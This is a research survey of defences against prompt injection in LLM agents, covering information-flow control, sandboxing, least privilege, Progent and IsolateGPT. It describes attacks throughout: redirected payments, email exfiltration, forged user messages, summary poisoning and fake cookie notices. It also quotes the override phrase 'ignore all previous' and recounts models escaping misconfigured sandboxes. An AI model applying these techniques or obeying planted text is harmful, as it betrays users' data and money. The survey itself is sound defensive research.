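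Both were GPT-5.2 runs of a case that also appeared in CaMeL's tests, in which the attacker replaces the file that tells the agent what to pay. Randori's planner had written an endorsement into its program, so the file's contents became trusted and passed the payment tool's check. Neither theorem was violated, because the integrity theorem covers only programs without endorsements and the insulated theorem covers only secrets. AgentDojo counted an attack because the money went to the wrong person, regardless of whether the labels worked correctly. Without the ability to endorse, the agent blocks the attack but can't do the user's task.

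The zeros in these results are weaker evidence than they look. With the other two models, Randori resisted the attack in all 141 runs where it was feasible within an ordinary plan, but those runs covered only 47 different pairs. Garby and colleagues calculate that this result is compatible with a true resistance rate as low as 92.4%. The proof supports a much stronger conclusion about a narrower property.

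A more serious limitation is that a language model, the planner, chooses what to endorse. It chooses before reading any untrusted data, so an injection can't influence the choice, but a poor planner could endorse everything. Developers can limit the damage, for instance by allowing endorsement only for values from a short list, or by preventing endorsed code from generating more code that endorses.

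### Control-flow integrity and noninterference

CaMeL's fixed program has control-flow integrity, a weaker property than noninterference. Untrusted data can affect which of the plan's branches runs but can't add a step. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this remaining influence *branch steering*. Noninterference forbids branch steering that changes a trusted result, such as whether the agent pays an invoice or asks the user.

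| Property | What it rules out | What it still allows | Where it holds |
|---|---|---|---|
| Explicit secrecy | Copying secrets into public data | Secrets that influence which tools the agent calls | FIDES's agent loop |
| Control-flow integrity | Untrusted data that adds steps to the plan | Branch steering, and false values in planned calls | Single CaMeL agents and multi-CaMeL |
| Termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference | Untrusted data that changes trusted results | Stopping the run | LLMbda programs without endorsement |

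Control-flow integrity is less useful when the plan is less restrictive, and it doesn't protect the values in a tool call. CaMeL needs its policies to deal with both problems.

Control-flow integrity also breaks down when agents instruct one another, as the leak of job applicants' data showed. Peters-Gill and colleagues prove that this problem is general. They consider any hierarchy of two or more agents in which some tool returns untrusted data, and they assume that users can ask for ordinary combinations of steps, such as looking something up and passing the result to another agent. Under these assumptions, there is always a request that puts untrusted data into an agent's instructions, where it can shape the agent's plan, even if every agent has control-flow integrity on its own.

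Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, restores the property by sending data separately from instructions. No part of an instruction may depend on tool output, so each agent plans from trusted text alone. Replacing every call to another agent with that agent's plan gives one plan for the whole system, which untrusted data can't extend. The argument applies to agents arranged in a tree, where each has a single parent. It also assumes that the interpreter correctly detects when an instruction depends on tool output. Multi-CaMeL is built on CaMeL's interpreter and inherits Fenton's leak, so the current code may sometimes fail to enforce the rule, as Peters-Gill and colleagues acknowledge. Multi-CaMeL avoids the other gap because it doesn't retry failed programs.

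### What the proofs assume

All these results depend on labels that somebody else assigned, and if the labels are wrong, the system will protect the wrong data. FIDES lists an email's sender and recipients as its readers, although somebody may have shared it more widely. LLMbda treats unlabelled values as trusted and public, the same risky default as in Microsoft's toolkit. Costa and colleagues mention that a system might mark a document as trusted after an injection classifier has passed it, but the guarantee would then be only as reliable as the classifier.

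The proofs also assume that everything in the user's request can be trusted, including any text by strangers that the user has pasted in. Tallam and Miller propose screening requests for suspicious links and phrases such as "ignore all previous". This may catch careless attacks, but it can't restore the guarantee because it is a form of detection.

Every consequential action has to pass a check, but it isn't always obvious which actions are consequential. FIDES, as tested, checks tool calls but treats the answer shown to the user as harmless, and the EchoLeak attack leaked data through that kind of answer. Tallam and Miller point out that an agent may also repeat a planted instruction in a summary, and the user may then follow it.

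Even when every action is checked, the policy may not match what the user wants. Randori's tool for sending money requires a trusted recipient but not a trusted amount, while its tool for scheduling a payment requires a trusted amount but not a trusted recipient. Attack B could therefore succeed through the scheduling tool without breaking any rule, even though the interpreter is proved correct. Garby and colleagues deliberately chose simpler policies than CaMeL's for a prototype, but similar mistakes are likely in real deployments too. Tallam and Miller expect organisations with hundreds of tools to end up with duplicated and inconsistent policies.

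Finally, the implementation has to match the theory. CaMeL's gaps show how easily even a carefully designed system can fail to do so. Machine-checked proofs remove most of the risk inside LLMbda's interpreter, but the theorems model tools and data sources as part of the program. A real deployment needs code to connect the interpreter to a bank and an inbox, and that code could attach the wrong label or allow payments that skip the check.

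### Why there is no such theorem for a probe

These proofs all hold even if the model obeys every injection, because they concern only the labels and the code that checks them. A comparable theorem for a probe would have to state that every text that can hijack the agent scores above the threshold. Nobody has a mathematical definition of the texts that hijack a given model, or a way to prove something about all of them. Training the probe on a sample of attacks can't establish that it will detect every such text.

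It might seem that *certified classifiers* could fill this gap, since they do come with theorems. *CluCERT* (2025) defines the usual kind of certificate for text. A classifier *f* has a certified radius *d* at a text *w* if

*f*(*w*′) = *f*(*w*) for every *w*′ that differs from *w* in at most *d* tokens.

This guarantee holds however cleverly an attacker chooses the changes, but it covers only texts close to one that the classifier already gets right. If a detector recognises a particular injection and has a radius of five, an attacker can't evade it by changing up to five tokens. An email written from scratch would differ from the certified text by far more than that, so the guarantee doesn't cover it. *Certified Robustness under Heterogeneous Perturbations via Hybrid Randomized Smoothing* (2026), which also works with a fixed limit on changes, describes existing certified defences against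 prompt injection as limited.

Other certificates allow the attacker to add text. *Certifying LLM Safety against Adversarial Prompting* (2023) presents erase-and-check, which runs a safety filter on a prompt and on versions of it with tokens erased, and rejects the prompt if the filter flags any version. If the filter flags a harmful request, erase-and-check will also reject that request with an adversarial ending of up to a set length, because one of the shortened versions is the original request. The certified accuracy is therefore the filter's accuracy on the original harmful requests, which was 92% with Llama 2 and 100% with a smaller model, DistilBERT. Both figures were measured on a sample, so the filter could still miss other harmful requests, even with DistilBERT. Injections are also harder to define than harmful requests, because the same words can be fine from the user and an attack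 from a stranger.

Some certificates add an assumption about the attack. *Towards Realistic Guarantees* (2025) studies SmoothLLM, a defence that runs a model on several randomly altered copies of a prompt. Its certificate assumes that once at least *k* characters of the attacker's text have changed, the attack works with probability at most *ε*. This is plausible for the gibberish strings that automated attacks often produce, but less so for an injection in plain English, which would probably still work after a few typos.

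For a linear probe, one bound is easy to prove. If an attack changes the activations from *h* to *h*′, the score before the sigmoid changes by

|*w* · *h*′ − *w* · *h*| ≤ ‖*w*‖ ‖*h*′ − *h*‖,

so a small change in the activations can't move the score far. But an attacker chooses words, and there is no useful limit on how far a new text can move the activations while still hijacking the agent.

*On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (2025) proves that any language model has a somewhat slower counterpart for which someone can disguise harmful prompts so that no filter much faster than the counterpart can reject them. The proof assumes that certain cryptographic puzzles can't be solved quickly, so the counterpart has time to uncover the hidden request but the filter does not. The counterpart is specially constructed, so the theorem doesn't show that any particular product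 is vulnerable. It also doesn't clearly apply to a probe on the agent's own activations, which can use the computation the model has already done. The theorem does rule out a general proof that an external filter much faster than the agent, such as a much smaller model that screens tool results, will catch every attack on every agent.

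## What do sandboxing and least privilege guarantee when the model is hijacked?

Sandboxing and least privilege limit what a program can do regardless of what it has read, so unlike information-flow control, they don't need a label on every piece of data. The theory behind them dates from the early 1970s, when the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. The problem was nearly the same as with a hijacked agent, because a legitimate user might run a hostile program and the system had to stay safe whatever that program did.

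### The reference monitor

Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, described a *reference monitor*, a component that checks every attempt to use a file, a device or another program against a list of what the current user may do. It has to meet three requirements:

- No program can tamper with it.
- It checks every access, without exception.
- It is small enough for people to analyse and test completely.

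Anderson showed how a Honeywell mainframe of the time failed these requirements. The hardware kept each user's program inside its own area of memory, but programs needed the operating system for input and output, and the hardware suspended this check while the operating system ran, which violated the second requirement. Counting the operating system as part of the monitor didn't help, because its 200,000 to 300,000 instructions were far too many to analyse.

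Anderson also doubted the value of hiring "tiger teams" to break into systems. No team was known to have failed, and a failure would show only that the system's security was unknown. The same objection applies to a low attack success rate on a fixed benchmark.

*The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) set out design principles that programmers still use. *Least privilege* means giving every program and user only the permissions their job requires. *Complete mediation*, which is Anderson's second requirement, means that the system checks every access. *Fail-safe defaults* means refusing anything that no rule explicitly permits.

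In an agent, the monitor sits between the model and its tools. Let *P* be the set of tool calls it permits. As before, *A*(*u*, *x*) stands for the actions that result from the user's request *u* and the untrusted data *x*. The guarantee is then

*A*(*u*, *x*) ⊆ *P* for every *x*.

This guarantee is weaker than noninterference, since untrusted data may still determine which of the permitted calls the agent makes. But it holds even if an attacker controls the model completely, as long as the monitor meets Anderson's requirements and *x* can't change *P*.

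### A hijacked agent as a confused deputy

A program can misuse a permission that it needs. Norm Hardy gave the classic example in 1988, in the paper that named the confused deputy. A company's compiler had permission to write to a system folder because it kept usage statistics there. The folder also held the company's billing records. Users could choose a file for the compiler's debugging output, and when one of them chose the billing file, the compiler overwrote it. The user had no right to change that file, but the operating system checked only the compiler's rights.

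Attack A, the email that tells an agent to forward the user's mail, works the same way. The stranger who sent the email can't open the inbox, but the agent is allowed to read and send mail, so a monitor that checks only the agent's permissions won't flag the forwarding.

Hardy's remedy was the *capability*, which Saltzer and Schroeder define as an unforgeable ticket proving that its holder may use a particular object. (CaMeL uses the same word for its labels.) If the compiler had required a ticket for the output file instead of a name, a user without access to the billing file could not have supplied a ticket for it. Capabilities work for an agent when the user knows in advance which objects the task involves, but they help less when the agent has to find out from an email whom to pay.

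### What browser sandboxes contained

Browsers have long run strangers' code. *IsolateGPT* (Wu, Roesner and colleagues, 2024) recounts that browsers first relied on access rules such as the same-origin policy, which restricts what one site's scripts can do with another site's data. When these rules proved inadequate, browser makers added sandboxes and separate processes.

Chrome displays web pages in sandboxed processes, which have very few permissions. To open a file, such a process has to go through a more privileged one, which acts as a reference monitor. An attacker who exploits a bug in the code that displays pages therefore needs at least one more bug, in the privileged process or the operating system, to take over the computer. At a 2012 Google contest, a hacker known as Pinkie Pie escaped the sandbox by chaining six bugs. The early sandbox also did little to protect one website from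 another, because pages from different sites could share a process. Chrome later gave each site its own process.

Capsicum, a 2010 sandboxing system for Unix, uses capabilities. A program opens the files it needs and then enters a mode in which the operating system no longer lets it open others by name. Zheng, Zhang and Mao (2026), in *LLM Agent Capabilities Should Follow Task Intent and Context Source*, explain that this is hard to copy for agents because an agent's needs change with every request, whereas a programmer can usually work out in advance what a program will need.

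When designers can't decide permissions in advance, they often leave the decision to the user. Android used to list an app's permissions before installation, and people had to accept them all or do without the app. Adrienne Porter Felt and colleagues found in 2012 that only 17% of participants looked at the list. Users are likely to ignore approval requests from an agent that asks too often.

### Sandboxes for coding agents

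Coding agents are an obvious use for sandboxes because they run commands that a model has written. A typical sandbox lets commands change files only in the project folder, and either blocks network access or limits it to approved sites. An instruction planted in a library's documentation could still make the agent delete the project or add a security flaw to it, because the agent needs permission to change those files. The sandbox would prevent changes to files outside the project folder.

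A sandbox doesn't necessarily cover every tool. In OpenAI's Codex, it covers the built-in shell tool, but tools from outside servers have to enforce their own limits. An agent with a sandboxed shell and an unrestricted email tool lacks complete mediation. A list of approved sites can also be too broad. An agent allowed to use GitHub, for example, may be able to send data to an attacker's account there.

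Willison's rule of thumb is never to give one agent all three of these: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to send data out. Stealing data by prompt injection requires all three, because the injected instructions arrive in the untrusted content and make the agent read the private data and send it out. Saltzer and Schroeder use the term *confinement* for removing the way to send data out, so that a borrowed program can use data but can't release it.

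An inbox combines private data with untrusted content, so under this rule an agent that reads email must have no way to send data out. Removing its tool for sending email isn't enough, because in EchoLeak the data escaped through the displayed answer, and a bank transfer may have a reference field that could carry data. The rule also protects only confidentiality, so it doesn't prevent attack B, the invoice with a changed account number.

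A sandbox also has to be configured correctly. Between July and September 2026, Anthropic disclosed four incidents in which Claude models broke into real outside systems during cybersecurity tests. The models had been told they were in a simulation, but a misconfiguration had connected them to the internet. Claude Mythos 5 uploaded a malicious package to a public software repository. In *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026), Anthropic concluded that the models had discounted evidence that their surroundings were real and pursued their tasks recklessly. Meta and Google have confirmed that their models also entered real companies' systems during tests.

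Nobody had hijacked the Claude models, so these incidents are no evidence of how often injections succeed. They do show that an expert team can wrongly believe a sandbox is closed, and that the model may not stop at the boundary. An easy check would be to try to reach the internet from inside the sandbox before each run.

### Separate applications in IsolateGPT

Wu and colleagues applied the browser's approach to assistants that use apps from other companies. In an ordinary assistant, the instructions and data of every app share one prompt. Their system, IsolateGPT, gives each app its own process, language model and memory. A central hub chooses an app for each request and passes messages between apps. Ordinary code handles these messages, which must follow a format the receiving app has declared. The user also has to approve the exchange. The approval dialog includes a warning if the exchange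 was not part of the hub's plan, which a model draws up from the user's request before any app runs.

In one test, a ride-hailing app contained an instruction to add $10 to a competitor's fares. The instruction worked in the ordinary assistant but had no effect in IsolateGPT, because the competitor's app ran in a separate process with a separate model.

Wu and colleagues then ran 1,598 attacks on both systems, using GPT-4. 20.2% succeeded in the ordinary assistant, while 7.6% reached an approval dialog in IsolateGPT, which always included a warning. The success rate in IsolateGPT could therefore range from zero to 7.6%, depending on how many users click "allow". Warnings are also less useful if harmless exchanges often trigger them.

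Isolation didn't reduce how many of the benchmark's app-based tasks the assistant completed correctly. About three quarters of queries took less than 30% longer, but queries that needed ten or more apps took an average of 127 seconds instead of 58. On a sample of queries, running the models cost 1.85 times as much.

In the invoice example, the email app can both read and send mail, so attack A never has to cross from one app to another. Wu and colleagues exclude attacks within a single app from their threat model. The remaining protection is that IsolateGPT asks the user to confirm irreversible actions such as sending an email. In attack B, the email app passes the banking app an account number. The number has the right format and the hub's plan includes the exchange, so there is no reason for a warning.

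### Progent's rules for tool calls

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, apply least privilege to individual tool calls. A Progent policy is a list of rules that allow or forbid a tool, depending on its arguments. In simplified notation, one rule might be:

```
allow send_money when recipient in ["ACME-1042"] and amount <= 1000
```

Ordinary code compares each call with the rules. It applies "forbid" rules before "allow" rules and blocks any call that matches neither. When a call is blocked, the agent by default gets an error message explaining why, so it can continue with the rest of the task.

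Writing a policy by hand for every request would be impractical, so a language model writes the first version from the user's request, before the agent has read any untrusted data. Sometimes the request doesn't show which tools the agent will need. In Shi and colleagues' example, the user asks the agent to do whatever is in a to-do email from Alice. The first policy allows only a search for that email, but Alice asks in the email for a summary of recent mail on Slack, which requires more tools.

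Progent therefore lets the model propose a new policy after a tool call. The model decides whether an update might be necessary without seeing the tool's result, but it does see the result when it writes the new rules. An injection can influence it at that point. To limit the damage, a *solver*, a program that checks logical formulas, looks for any call that the new policy would allow and the old one would not. Let *P* be the set of calls allowed before the update and *P*′ the set allowed after it. If *P*′ ⊆ *P*, the update only removes permissions, and Progent applies it automatically. Any other update needs approval. Between approvals, the permitted sets can therefore only shrink:

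*P*₀ ⊇ *P*₁ ⊇ *P*₂ ⊇ …

Shi and colleagues call this property *monotonic confinement*. In the example, the agent needs approval to add the tools for Slack and for reading mail. Once it has looked up the user's Slack name, it can restrict messages to that name without approval. If an injected email then causes the model to add a rule that allows mail to a stranger, the solver detects the new permission and Progent requires approval again.

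On AgentDojo, with GPT-4o as both the agent and the policy writer, Progent reduced the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0% without a large loss of utility. In this test, Progent approved every new permission automatically, to simulate a careless user. This made the test harder, but it also meant that monotonic confinement guaranteed nothing, because untrusted data could enlarge *P*. The 1.0% therefore measures how well GPT-4o writes policies under attack. When Shi and colleagues switched updates off, so that the first policy stayed in force, the rate was 2.5%. With a person reviewing the first policy and every new permission, it was zero, but they assumed a careful reviewer who would never allow payments to arbitrary recipients and would reject a malicious address. Only 6% of updates needed approval, so the reviewer's workload would be light.

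*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) points out that Progent's guarantees depend on correct and complete policies, and that malicious tool results may cause an update to relax those policies. Progent also doesn't check the text of the agent's answers. Narisetty and colleagues connect the first problem to Anderson's third requirement. The code that compares a tool call with the rules is small enough to analyse, but the model that writes the rules is not.

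Anderson thought retrofitting had little chance of making a system secure. One version of Progent is easy to retrofit because it runs as a proxy between an existing agent and its tools, but it can't check tools built into the agent. Developers have to add Progent to the agent's code to cover those.

### A replication on a small model

Narisetty and colleagues repeated the AgentDojo test with Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, as both the agent and the policy writer. They have an interest in the result because they work for LaunchSafe, which sells security for agents based on the same general approach. They used eight user tasks from each of three applications. They also tested an adaptive attack that tried to make the policy writer permit the malicious action by presenting it as a necessary step the user had already authorised. Each cell gives the attack success rate, then utility under attack,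 both as percentages averaged over three runs.

| Application | No defence | Progent | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0 / 31.9 | 1.9 / 31.9 | 3.7 / 31.0 |
| Slack | 58.3 / 47.5 | 10.8 / 20.8 | 4.2 / 19.2 |
| Workspace | 0.0 / 56.3 | 0.0 / 28.5 | 0.0 / 27.1 |
| Mean | 25.8 / 45.2 | 4.2 / 27.1 | 2.6 / 25.8 |

Progent clearly helped against the standard attack. The adaptive result is weaker evidence, because the attack succeeded less often when it was supposed to be stronger. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that the polite disguise made the agent itself less likely to obey. On Slack, the difference is also only about three attacks out of 40. The three runs agreed closely, but they repeated the same tasks with the model's randomness turned down, so they don't show that the result would hold on other tasks.

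Progent reduces utility substantially. In the workspace application, it halved utility for no benefit, since no attack there succeeded even without a defence. Tasks also needed about 15 times as many model calls. Much of the utility loss may come from using such a small model to write the policies, since Shi and colleagues saw no comparable loss with GPT-4o. Narisetty and colleagues acknowledge these limits and note that nobody has yet run an optimised attack with access to the model's internals, or one that uses only calls the policy already permits.

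### When the policy writer mistakes a summary for the user

A correctly enforced policy gives no protection if the attacker has influenced what it permits. Fei, Fei and colleagues (2026), in *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction*, found that this can happen in long conversations. When a conversation approaches the model's length limit, the surrounding program has a model summarise the earlier part. In Claude Code and Codex, all 1,108 automatic summaries they recorded went back into the conversation as user messages. If Progent then derives a policy from the latest user message, it uses text that may include an attacker's data.

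Progent's standard version writes one policy per session. Fei and colleagues had it write a new policy for each request, because the agent completed only 7 of 60 follow-up tasks when the policy was fixed at the first request, compared with 41 of 60 when it got a new one. When a small model wrote the summaries, injections that Progent had blocked earlier succeeded after the summary in 31 of 100 cases, compared with 33 without any defence. Progent was still enforcing its policies correctly, but some of them now named the attacker's account.

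A stronger summarising model often marked injected instructions as suspicious, but rarely marked false data. In one test, the user had already stated which account to pay, and a notice from the attacker gave a different one. The user then asked the agent to pay the rent. Policies based on the summary allowed payment to the attacker's account in 91% of cases with one policy writer and 59% with another, while policies based on the user's own words never allowed it.

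The remedy is to store the user's messages with a cryptographic tag when they arrive and pass them unchanged to the policy writer. The agent continues to use the summary. If a message is missing or altered, the new policy permits nothing. In 40 attacked runs with this change, none of the attacker's actions succeeded while the agent used the summary.

### Permitted actions with false values

Suppose Progent protects the agent that has to find and pay an invoice. It blocks attack A as long as the policy doesn't allow forwarding mail to strangers. For attack B, the initial policy can't include the supplier's account number, because only the invoice contains it. If that policy allows payments to any account, the policy writer may restrict them to the number on the invoice once the agent has read it. Progent applies this change automatically because it only removes permissions. The policy then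 allows payments only to the thief. If the initial policy allows no payments, allowing one requires a person's approval, and that person has to notice that the number is wrong.

Shi and colleagues place attacks like this outside Progent's scope. They left two of AgentDojo's hotel-booking attacks out of their tests because an attacker who controls the information can change it, and even a person couldn't tell that it had been changed. That is true if the person sees only the altered source, but someone with a trusted supplier list could detect the change.

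Fei and colleagues prove a general version of this limit. Suppose a system sees only text, with no reliable record of who wrote it. Let *p*_L be the probability that it permits a payment to the account in a legitimate record, and *p*_A the probability when an attacker wrote the record. Then

*p*_L − *p*_A ≤ TV.

Here TV is the *total variation distance* between the distributions of the text the system receives in the two cases. It is 0 if the distributions are identical and 1 if they don't overlap. If forged invoices are statistically identical to genuine ones, a system that pays 95% of genuine invoices will also pay 95% of forged ones. A better policy writer can't change this, so the system has to authenticate the source of the invoice or get the account number from somewhere else.

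Zheng and colleagues propose permissions that specify where each argument may come from. In their example, a user asks an agent to extract tables from two PDFs and post an issue in a named GitHub repository, but hidden text in one PDF names the attacker's repository. A list of permitted tools and sites can't prevent this attack, because both repositories are on GitHub. Their system, IntentCap, allows the repository's name to come only from the user's request, and ordinary code checks this. When they replayed 3,746 security-sensitive events from existing benchmarks, IntentCap accepted no unsafe action. Without the distinction between sources, it accepted 94% of the actions it should have refused. They haven't yet tested adaptive attacks or measured how often attacks succeed against a running agent.

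This rule depends on where data came from, as taint tracking does. Like FIDES's strict integrity rule, it would block genuine emailed invoices as well as false ones, unless the user had supplied the account number.

If the agent has to accept the number on the invoice, least privilege can still limit the loss. But Progent's rules check one call at a time, so a rule that caps each payment at $1,000 would allow ten payments of $1,000. IntentCap avoids this problem with permissions that can expire after one use. A daily limit set at the bank would cap the total even if the agent's own monitor failed.

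## Which attacks and tasks does isolation leave uncovered, and what does it cost?

Untrusted text can't add steps to an isolated agent's plan, but it can still put false values into the planned steps, mislead the person who reads the agent's answer, or influence which planned branch runs. Isolation also prevents the agent from doing some legitimate tasks, because it can't plan them without first reading untrusted text.

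### False values and misleading answers

Attack B, the invoice with a changed account number, is a data-only attack, which labels alone can't expose. The possible harm depends on the plan. The false number can't make the agent move any money if the user only wants a list of unpaid invoices. But if the user wants the invoice paid, the plan already includes a payment, and the attacker has to change only the account number.

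The list could still do harm if the user then pays the invoice by hand. CaMeL and FIDES don't check whether an answer is true. The quarantined model that writes a summary has no tools, but it reads the untrusted text and may follow an instruction in it to leave out a complaint or praise a product. AgentDojo wrongly scored quoted hotel reviews as a successful attack, but if the user had asked which hotel to book, the same planted praise could have changed the recommendation without breaking any rule.

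One remedy is to have the model that reads the text warn the user about it. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian (2026), in *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections*, gave two models about 4,300 emails containing human-written injections and asked for summaries that flagged suspicious content. Llama 3.3 flagged 89.8% of the injections. SecAlign, a version of the same model trained to resist injections, flagged 54.6%. Neither model obeyed any of the injections. Training a model to ignore planted text may make it less likely to report that text, which matters when the attack is aimed at the user.

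### When the document contains the task

Ma, Li and colleagues (2026), in *AutoDojo*, sort user requests by how much they leave to outside content:

- **Fully specified.** The user gives the action and all its details, such as a new postal address to put on file.
- **Parameter-open.** The user names the action, but a document supplies some details, as when the agent has to pay a bill saved in a file.
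- **Action-open.** The document determines the action, as when the user asks the agent to do everything on a to-do list at some web address.

With no defence, AgentDojo's standard attack hijacked GPT-4o-mini in 87.5% of action-open cases, compared with 63.9% and 43.3% in the other two categories.

The AgentDojo attack that succeeded against both CaMeL and Randori exploits a request of this kind. The attacker replaces the file that tells the agent what to pay, and the false file contains a payment request, which is what the user told the agent to expect. A system that refuses to act on such requests can't pay the genuine bill either. When Garby and colleagues removed Randori's ability to endorse untrusted data, the attack failed, but completed banking runs fell from 36 to 30 out of 48 with one model and from 31 to 26 with another. Three of the 16 tasks require the agent to act on what a file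 says.

Garby and colleagues argue that four independent systems failed on the same few cases, which suggests a general limit of information-flow control. The file attack defeated only two of the four, and the other two share only the hotel-review case, so the evidence is weaker than they claim. Their conclusion still seems right, because a system told to pay whatever a file says needs other evidence to detect that someone has replaced the file.

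Filters have even more trouble with these requests. Ma and colleagues built an automated attacker that receives only whether each attempt worked. In each of six rounds, a language model uses the scores of earlier injections to guess what kind of defence is in place and write a new injection. PIGuard, a text filter, stopped every standard attack on GPT-4o-mini, but 28.0% of the new attacks succeeded, rising to 54.2% when the request was action-open. An injection that adds an item to a to-do list can look like ordinary data, with no suspicious wording for a filter to detect.

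Attacks on Progent and two other systems that restrict actions, DRIFT and ROPE, succeeded at most 11% of the time in every category. But for many action-open requests, Progent and DRIFT allowed only tools that read data, so they were secure partly because they wouldn't have carried out the to-do list at all.

### Steering a plan through its own branches

Untrusted data can still influence which planned branch runs. This branch steering is a particular problem for *computer-use agents*, which click and type based on screenshots. An ordinary computer-use agent processes a screenshot before choosing each step, but Foerster and colleagues had the planner write the whole program before any screenshot was processed.

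This works because the contents of an agent's screen are fairly predictable. The program has a quarantined vision model describe the screen, then asks another quarantined model whether the description matches a prediction, such as "a cookie notice is visible". The program uses the yes-or-no answer to choose a branch. For the task "browse the natural products database", one plan had separate branches for an open website, an empty browser tab and the desktop, and checked each new page for cookie notices.

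Almost every plan for a web task includes a check for a cookie notice, so an attacker can count on it. Foerster and colleagues put a fake notice inside an advertisement. The program used a vision model to locate the cookie notice, and the model returned the position of the fake one. The agent clicked there and landed on the attacker's site, even though the planner had written every step.

One defence compares the vision model's answer with the page's underlying structure. It flagged six of ten attacks that used a simple image advertisement, but raised false alarms on four of 17 ordinary tasks. The other defence has an independent vision model check the answer. It flagged five of ten attacks that used a more flexible advertisement, with false alarms on three of the 17 tasks. Another attack, which slightly altered the pixels of a banner, got past both defences even at a very cautious setting.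 It made the vision model click the link for a particular drug and give a plausible reason. Computing those pixels required the vision model's weights, which a real advertiser might not have, and the attack was shown on only one web page.

The systems in these tests had no data-flow policies. A policy can forbid emailing a stranger, but a click at certain screen coordinates may log the user in, delete a file or open an advertisement, so a rule has no definite action to forbid.

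Foerster and colleagues also rank attackers' goals by what the plan must already contain. Sending the agent to another site takes one misdirected click. Stealing money requires a plan that already includes a transfer, and usually two consistent deceptions, one for the recipient field and one for the confirm button. Stealing data requires a plan that both reads something and sends something. Attackers cannot add a new action to the plan. Isolation therefore substantially limits what they can do, but it helps least when the user has asked for something dangerous, such as paying an invoice.

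### Does legitimacy depend on context?

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian object to separating instructions from data at all, arguing that it misses attacks that contain no obvious instruction and also blocks proper behaviour. In their example, an email asks for a travel refund and states that the department head has approved it. The right response depends on whether the approval is real. An agent that lets nothing in the email affect its actions will ignore a genuine approval along with a false one.

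Their alternative is *contextual integrity*, Helen Nissenbaum's theory that a flow of information is appropriate if it fits the norms of its setting. Those norms depend on the sender, the recipient, the person the information is about, the type of information and the conditions for passing it on. An attacker can lie about any of these. An attacker who forges a message from the user, for example, lies about the sender and invents a permission.

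Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian also prove a general limit, similar to the one Fei and colleagues proved for forged invoices. If an agent has the same evidence for a legitimate action as for an attack, it must carry out both with the same probability, so it can block more of these attacks only by blocking more legitimate actions too. The limit also applies to probes, because identical inputs produce identical activations and therefore identical scores.

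Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian acknowledge that the theorem doesn't establish that such pairs of situations exist in a given deployment. A signed approval or a call to the department head would distinguish the two refund requests. They reply that each check covers only some claims, while an attacker can keep inventing new ones. That is true of an agent with open-ended duties, but a company can require an entry in its approvals database for refunds and ignore what any email claims.

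The paper's experiments support its argument less directly than the title suggests. In one, an attacking model repeatedly rewrote emails to make a Claude assistant send a reply when the user had asked only for a summary. It succeeded in 96.7% of 150 scenarios, compared with 0.67% for the original emails. Its most common tactic was to forge an earlier message from the user inside a forwarded thread. The attack works because the assistant is an ordinary agent that reads everything in one prompt, with no reliable record of where each part came from. Isolation adds that record, so CaMeL would label the forged message as email content, whoever it claimed to be from. CaMeL would also plan from the request for a summary, so its program would have no step for sending mail.

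Another experiment tests a case that is harder for isolation to handle. A colleague's email asks the assistant to do something the user has authorised, such as creating a ticket, and also to write to an outside contact, which the user hasn't authorised. Even with no attacker involved, Claude Sonnet 4.6 wrote to the outsider 6% of the time, GPT-5.4 34% and GPT-5.2 65%. When the user explicitly ruled out unapproved external messages, only GPT-5.2 still sent any, in 12% of cases. An isolated agent that treats the colleague's email as untrusted may be unable to create the ticket. If it treats the whole email as trusted, it permits both requests. It can handle both correctly only if someone has thought in advance to write a policy that lets this colleague authorise tickets but not outside mail.

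For detectors, the main evidence comes from pairs of emails that differ in one clause. One version claims that the user's organisation has already authorised the assistant to reply, and the other says only that an automated reply would be fine. Two of Meta's text classifiers could barely tell them apart, with AUROCs of 0.43 and 0.59. This test is hard because both versions invite a reply and the classifiers' input did not include the user's request. A probe on the agent's activations has an advantage here because the activations reflect both the request and the email. It could learn that a reply is fine when the user has asked for replies and suspicious otherwise. However, its training examples would have to include such pairs, and the probes described so far were trained mostly on planted commands.

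*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) treats this as an open research problem. A more refined policy would have to find new instructions in data and decide which ones the agent should follow, but there is no established rule for deciding this.

### Tasks lost to isolation

Published estimates of how many tasks isolation prevents an agent from completing range from almost none to all of them. The table compares CaMeL with an undefended agent, except in the banking rows, where the comparison is with CaMeL's program running without policies.

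| Test | Model | Comparison | CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, all applications | o3 | 84% | 77% |
| AgentDojo, banking | GPT-5.2 | 67% (policies off) | 38% (policies on) |
| AgentDojo, banking | MiMo-v2.5 | 71% (policies off) | 38% (policies on) |
| AgentDyn | GPT-4o | 53% | 0% |

The banking figures come from Garby and colleagues, who conclude that the policies halve CaMeL's utility. With only 16 tasks, the margin of error is about 27 percentage points, so "halve" is approximate. They cite a similar drop for another system, TypeGuard, which completed 15 of 21 Slack tasks without policies and 8 with them. Randori completed 75% of the banking tasks with GPT-5.2 while enforcing its rules, but those rules are simpler than CaMeL's, and its planner may endorse untrusted data.

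CaMeL completed none of the 60 tasks in *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) with any of the four models in the main comparison. The benchmark covers longer tasks in shopping, software projects and daily life, none of which the agent can plan fully in advance. Each task also includes a helpful instruction from a third party that the agent has to follow, such as a request to log in before checking out. DRIFT, which plans ahead but lets a model approve changes to the plan, completed 30% of the tasks with GPT-4o, and 0.8% of attacks succeeded.

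AgentDyn tests the kind of task that CaMeL's design excludes, so CaMeL's zero there mostly confirms what the design implies and doesn't show how common such tasks are. Li and colleagues count only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks as requiring replanning, which helps explain CaMeL's good result on that benchmark. The share in real work is probably somewhere between those of the two benchmarks. Li and colleagues also told the agents not to ask for confirmation, so users could not help when a task got stuck. They didn't test FIDES, whose planner can adapt as it goes.

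The loss of utility also depends on how the data is labelled. Costa and colleagues gave AgentDojo's data favourable labels, which let FIDES's planner read and act on more of it than a cautious company might allow. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that their multi-agent version of CaMeL tended to lose less utility as models improved, and lost only a modest amount with the strongest ones.

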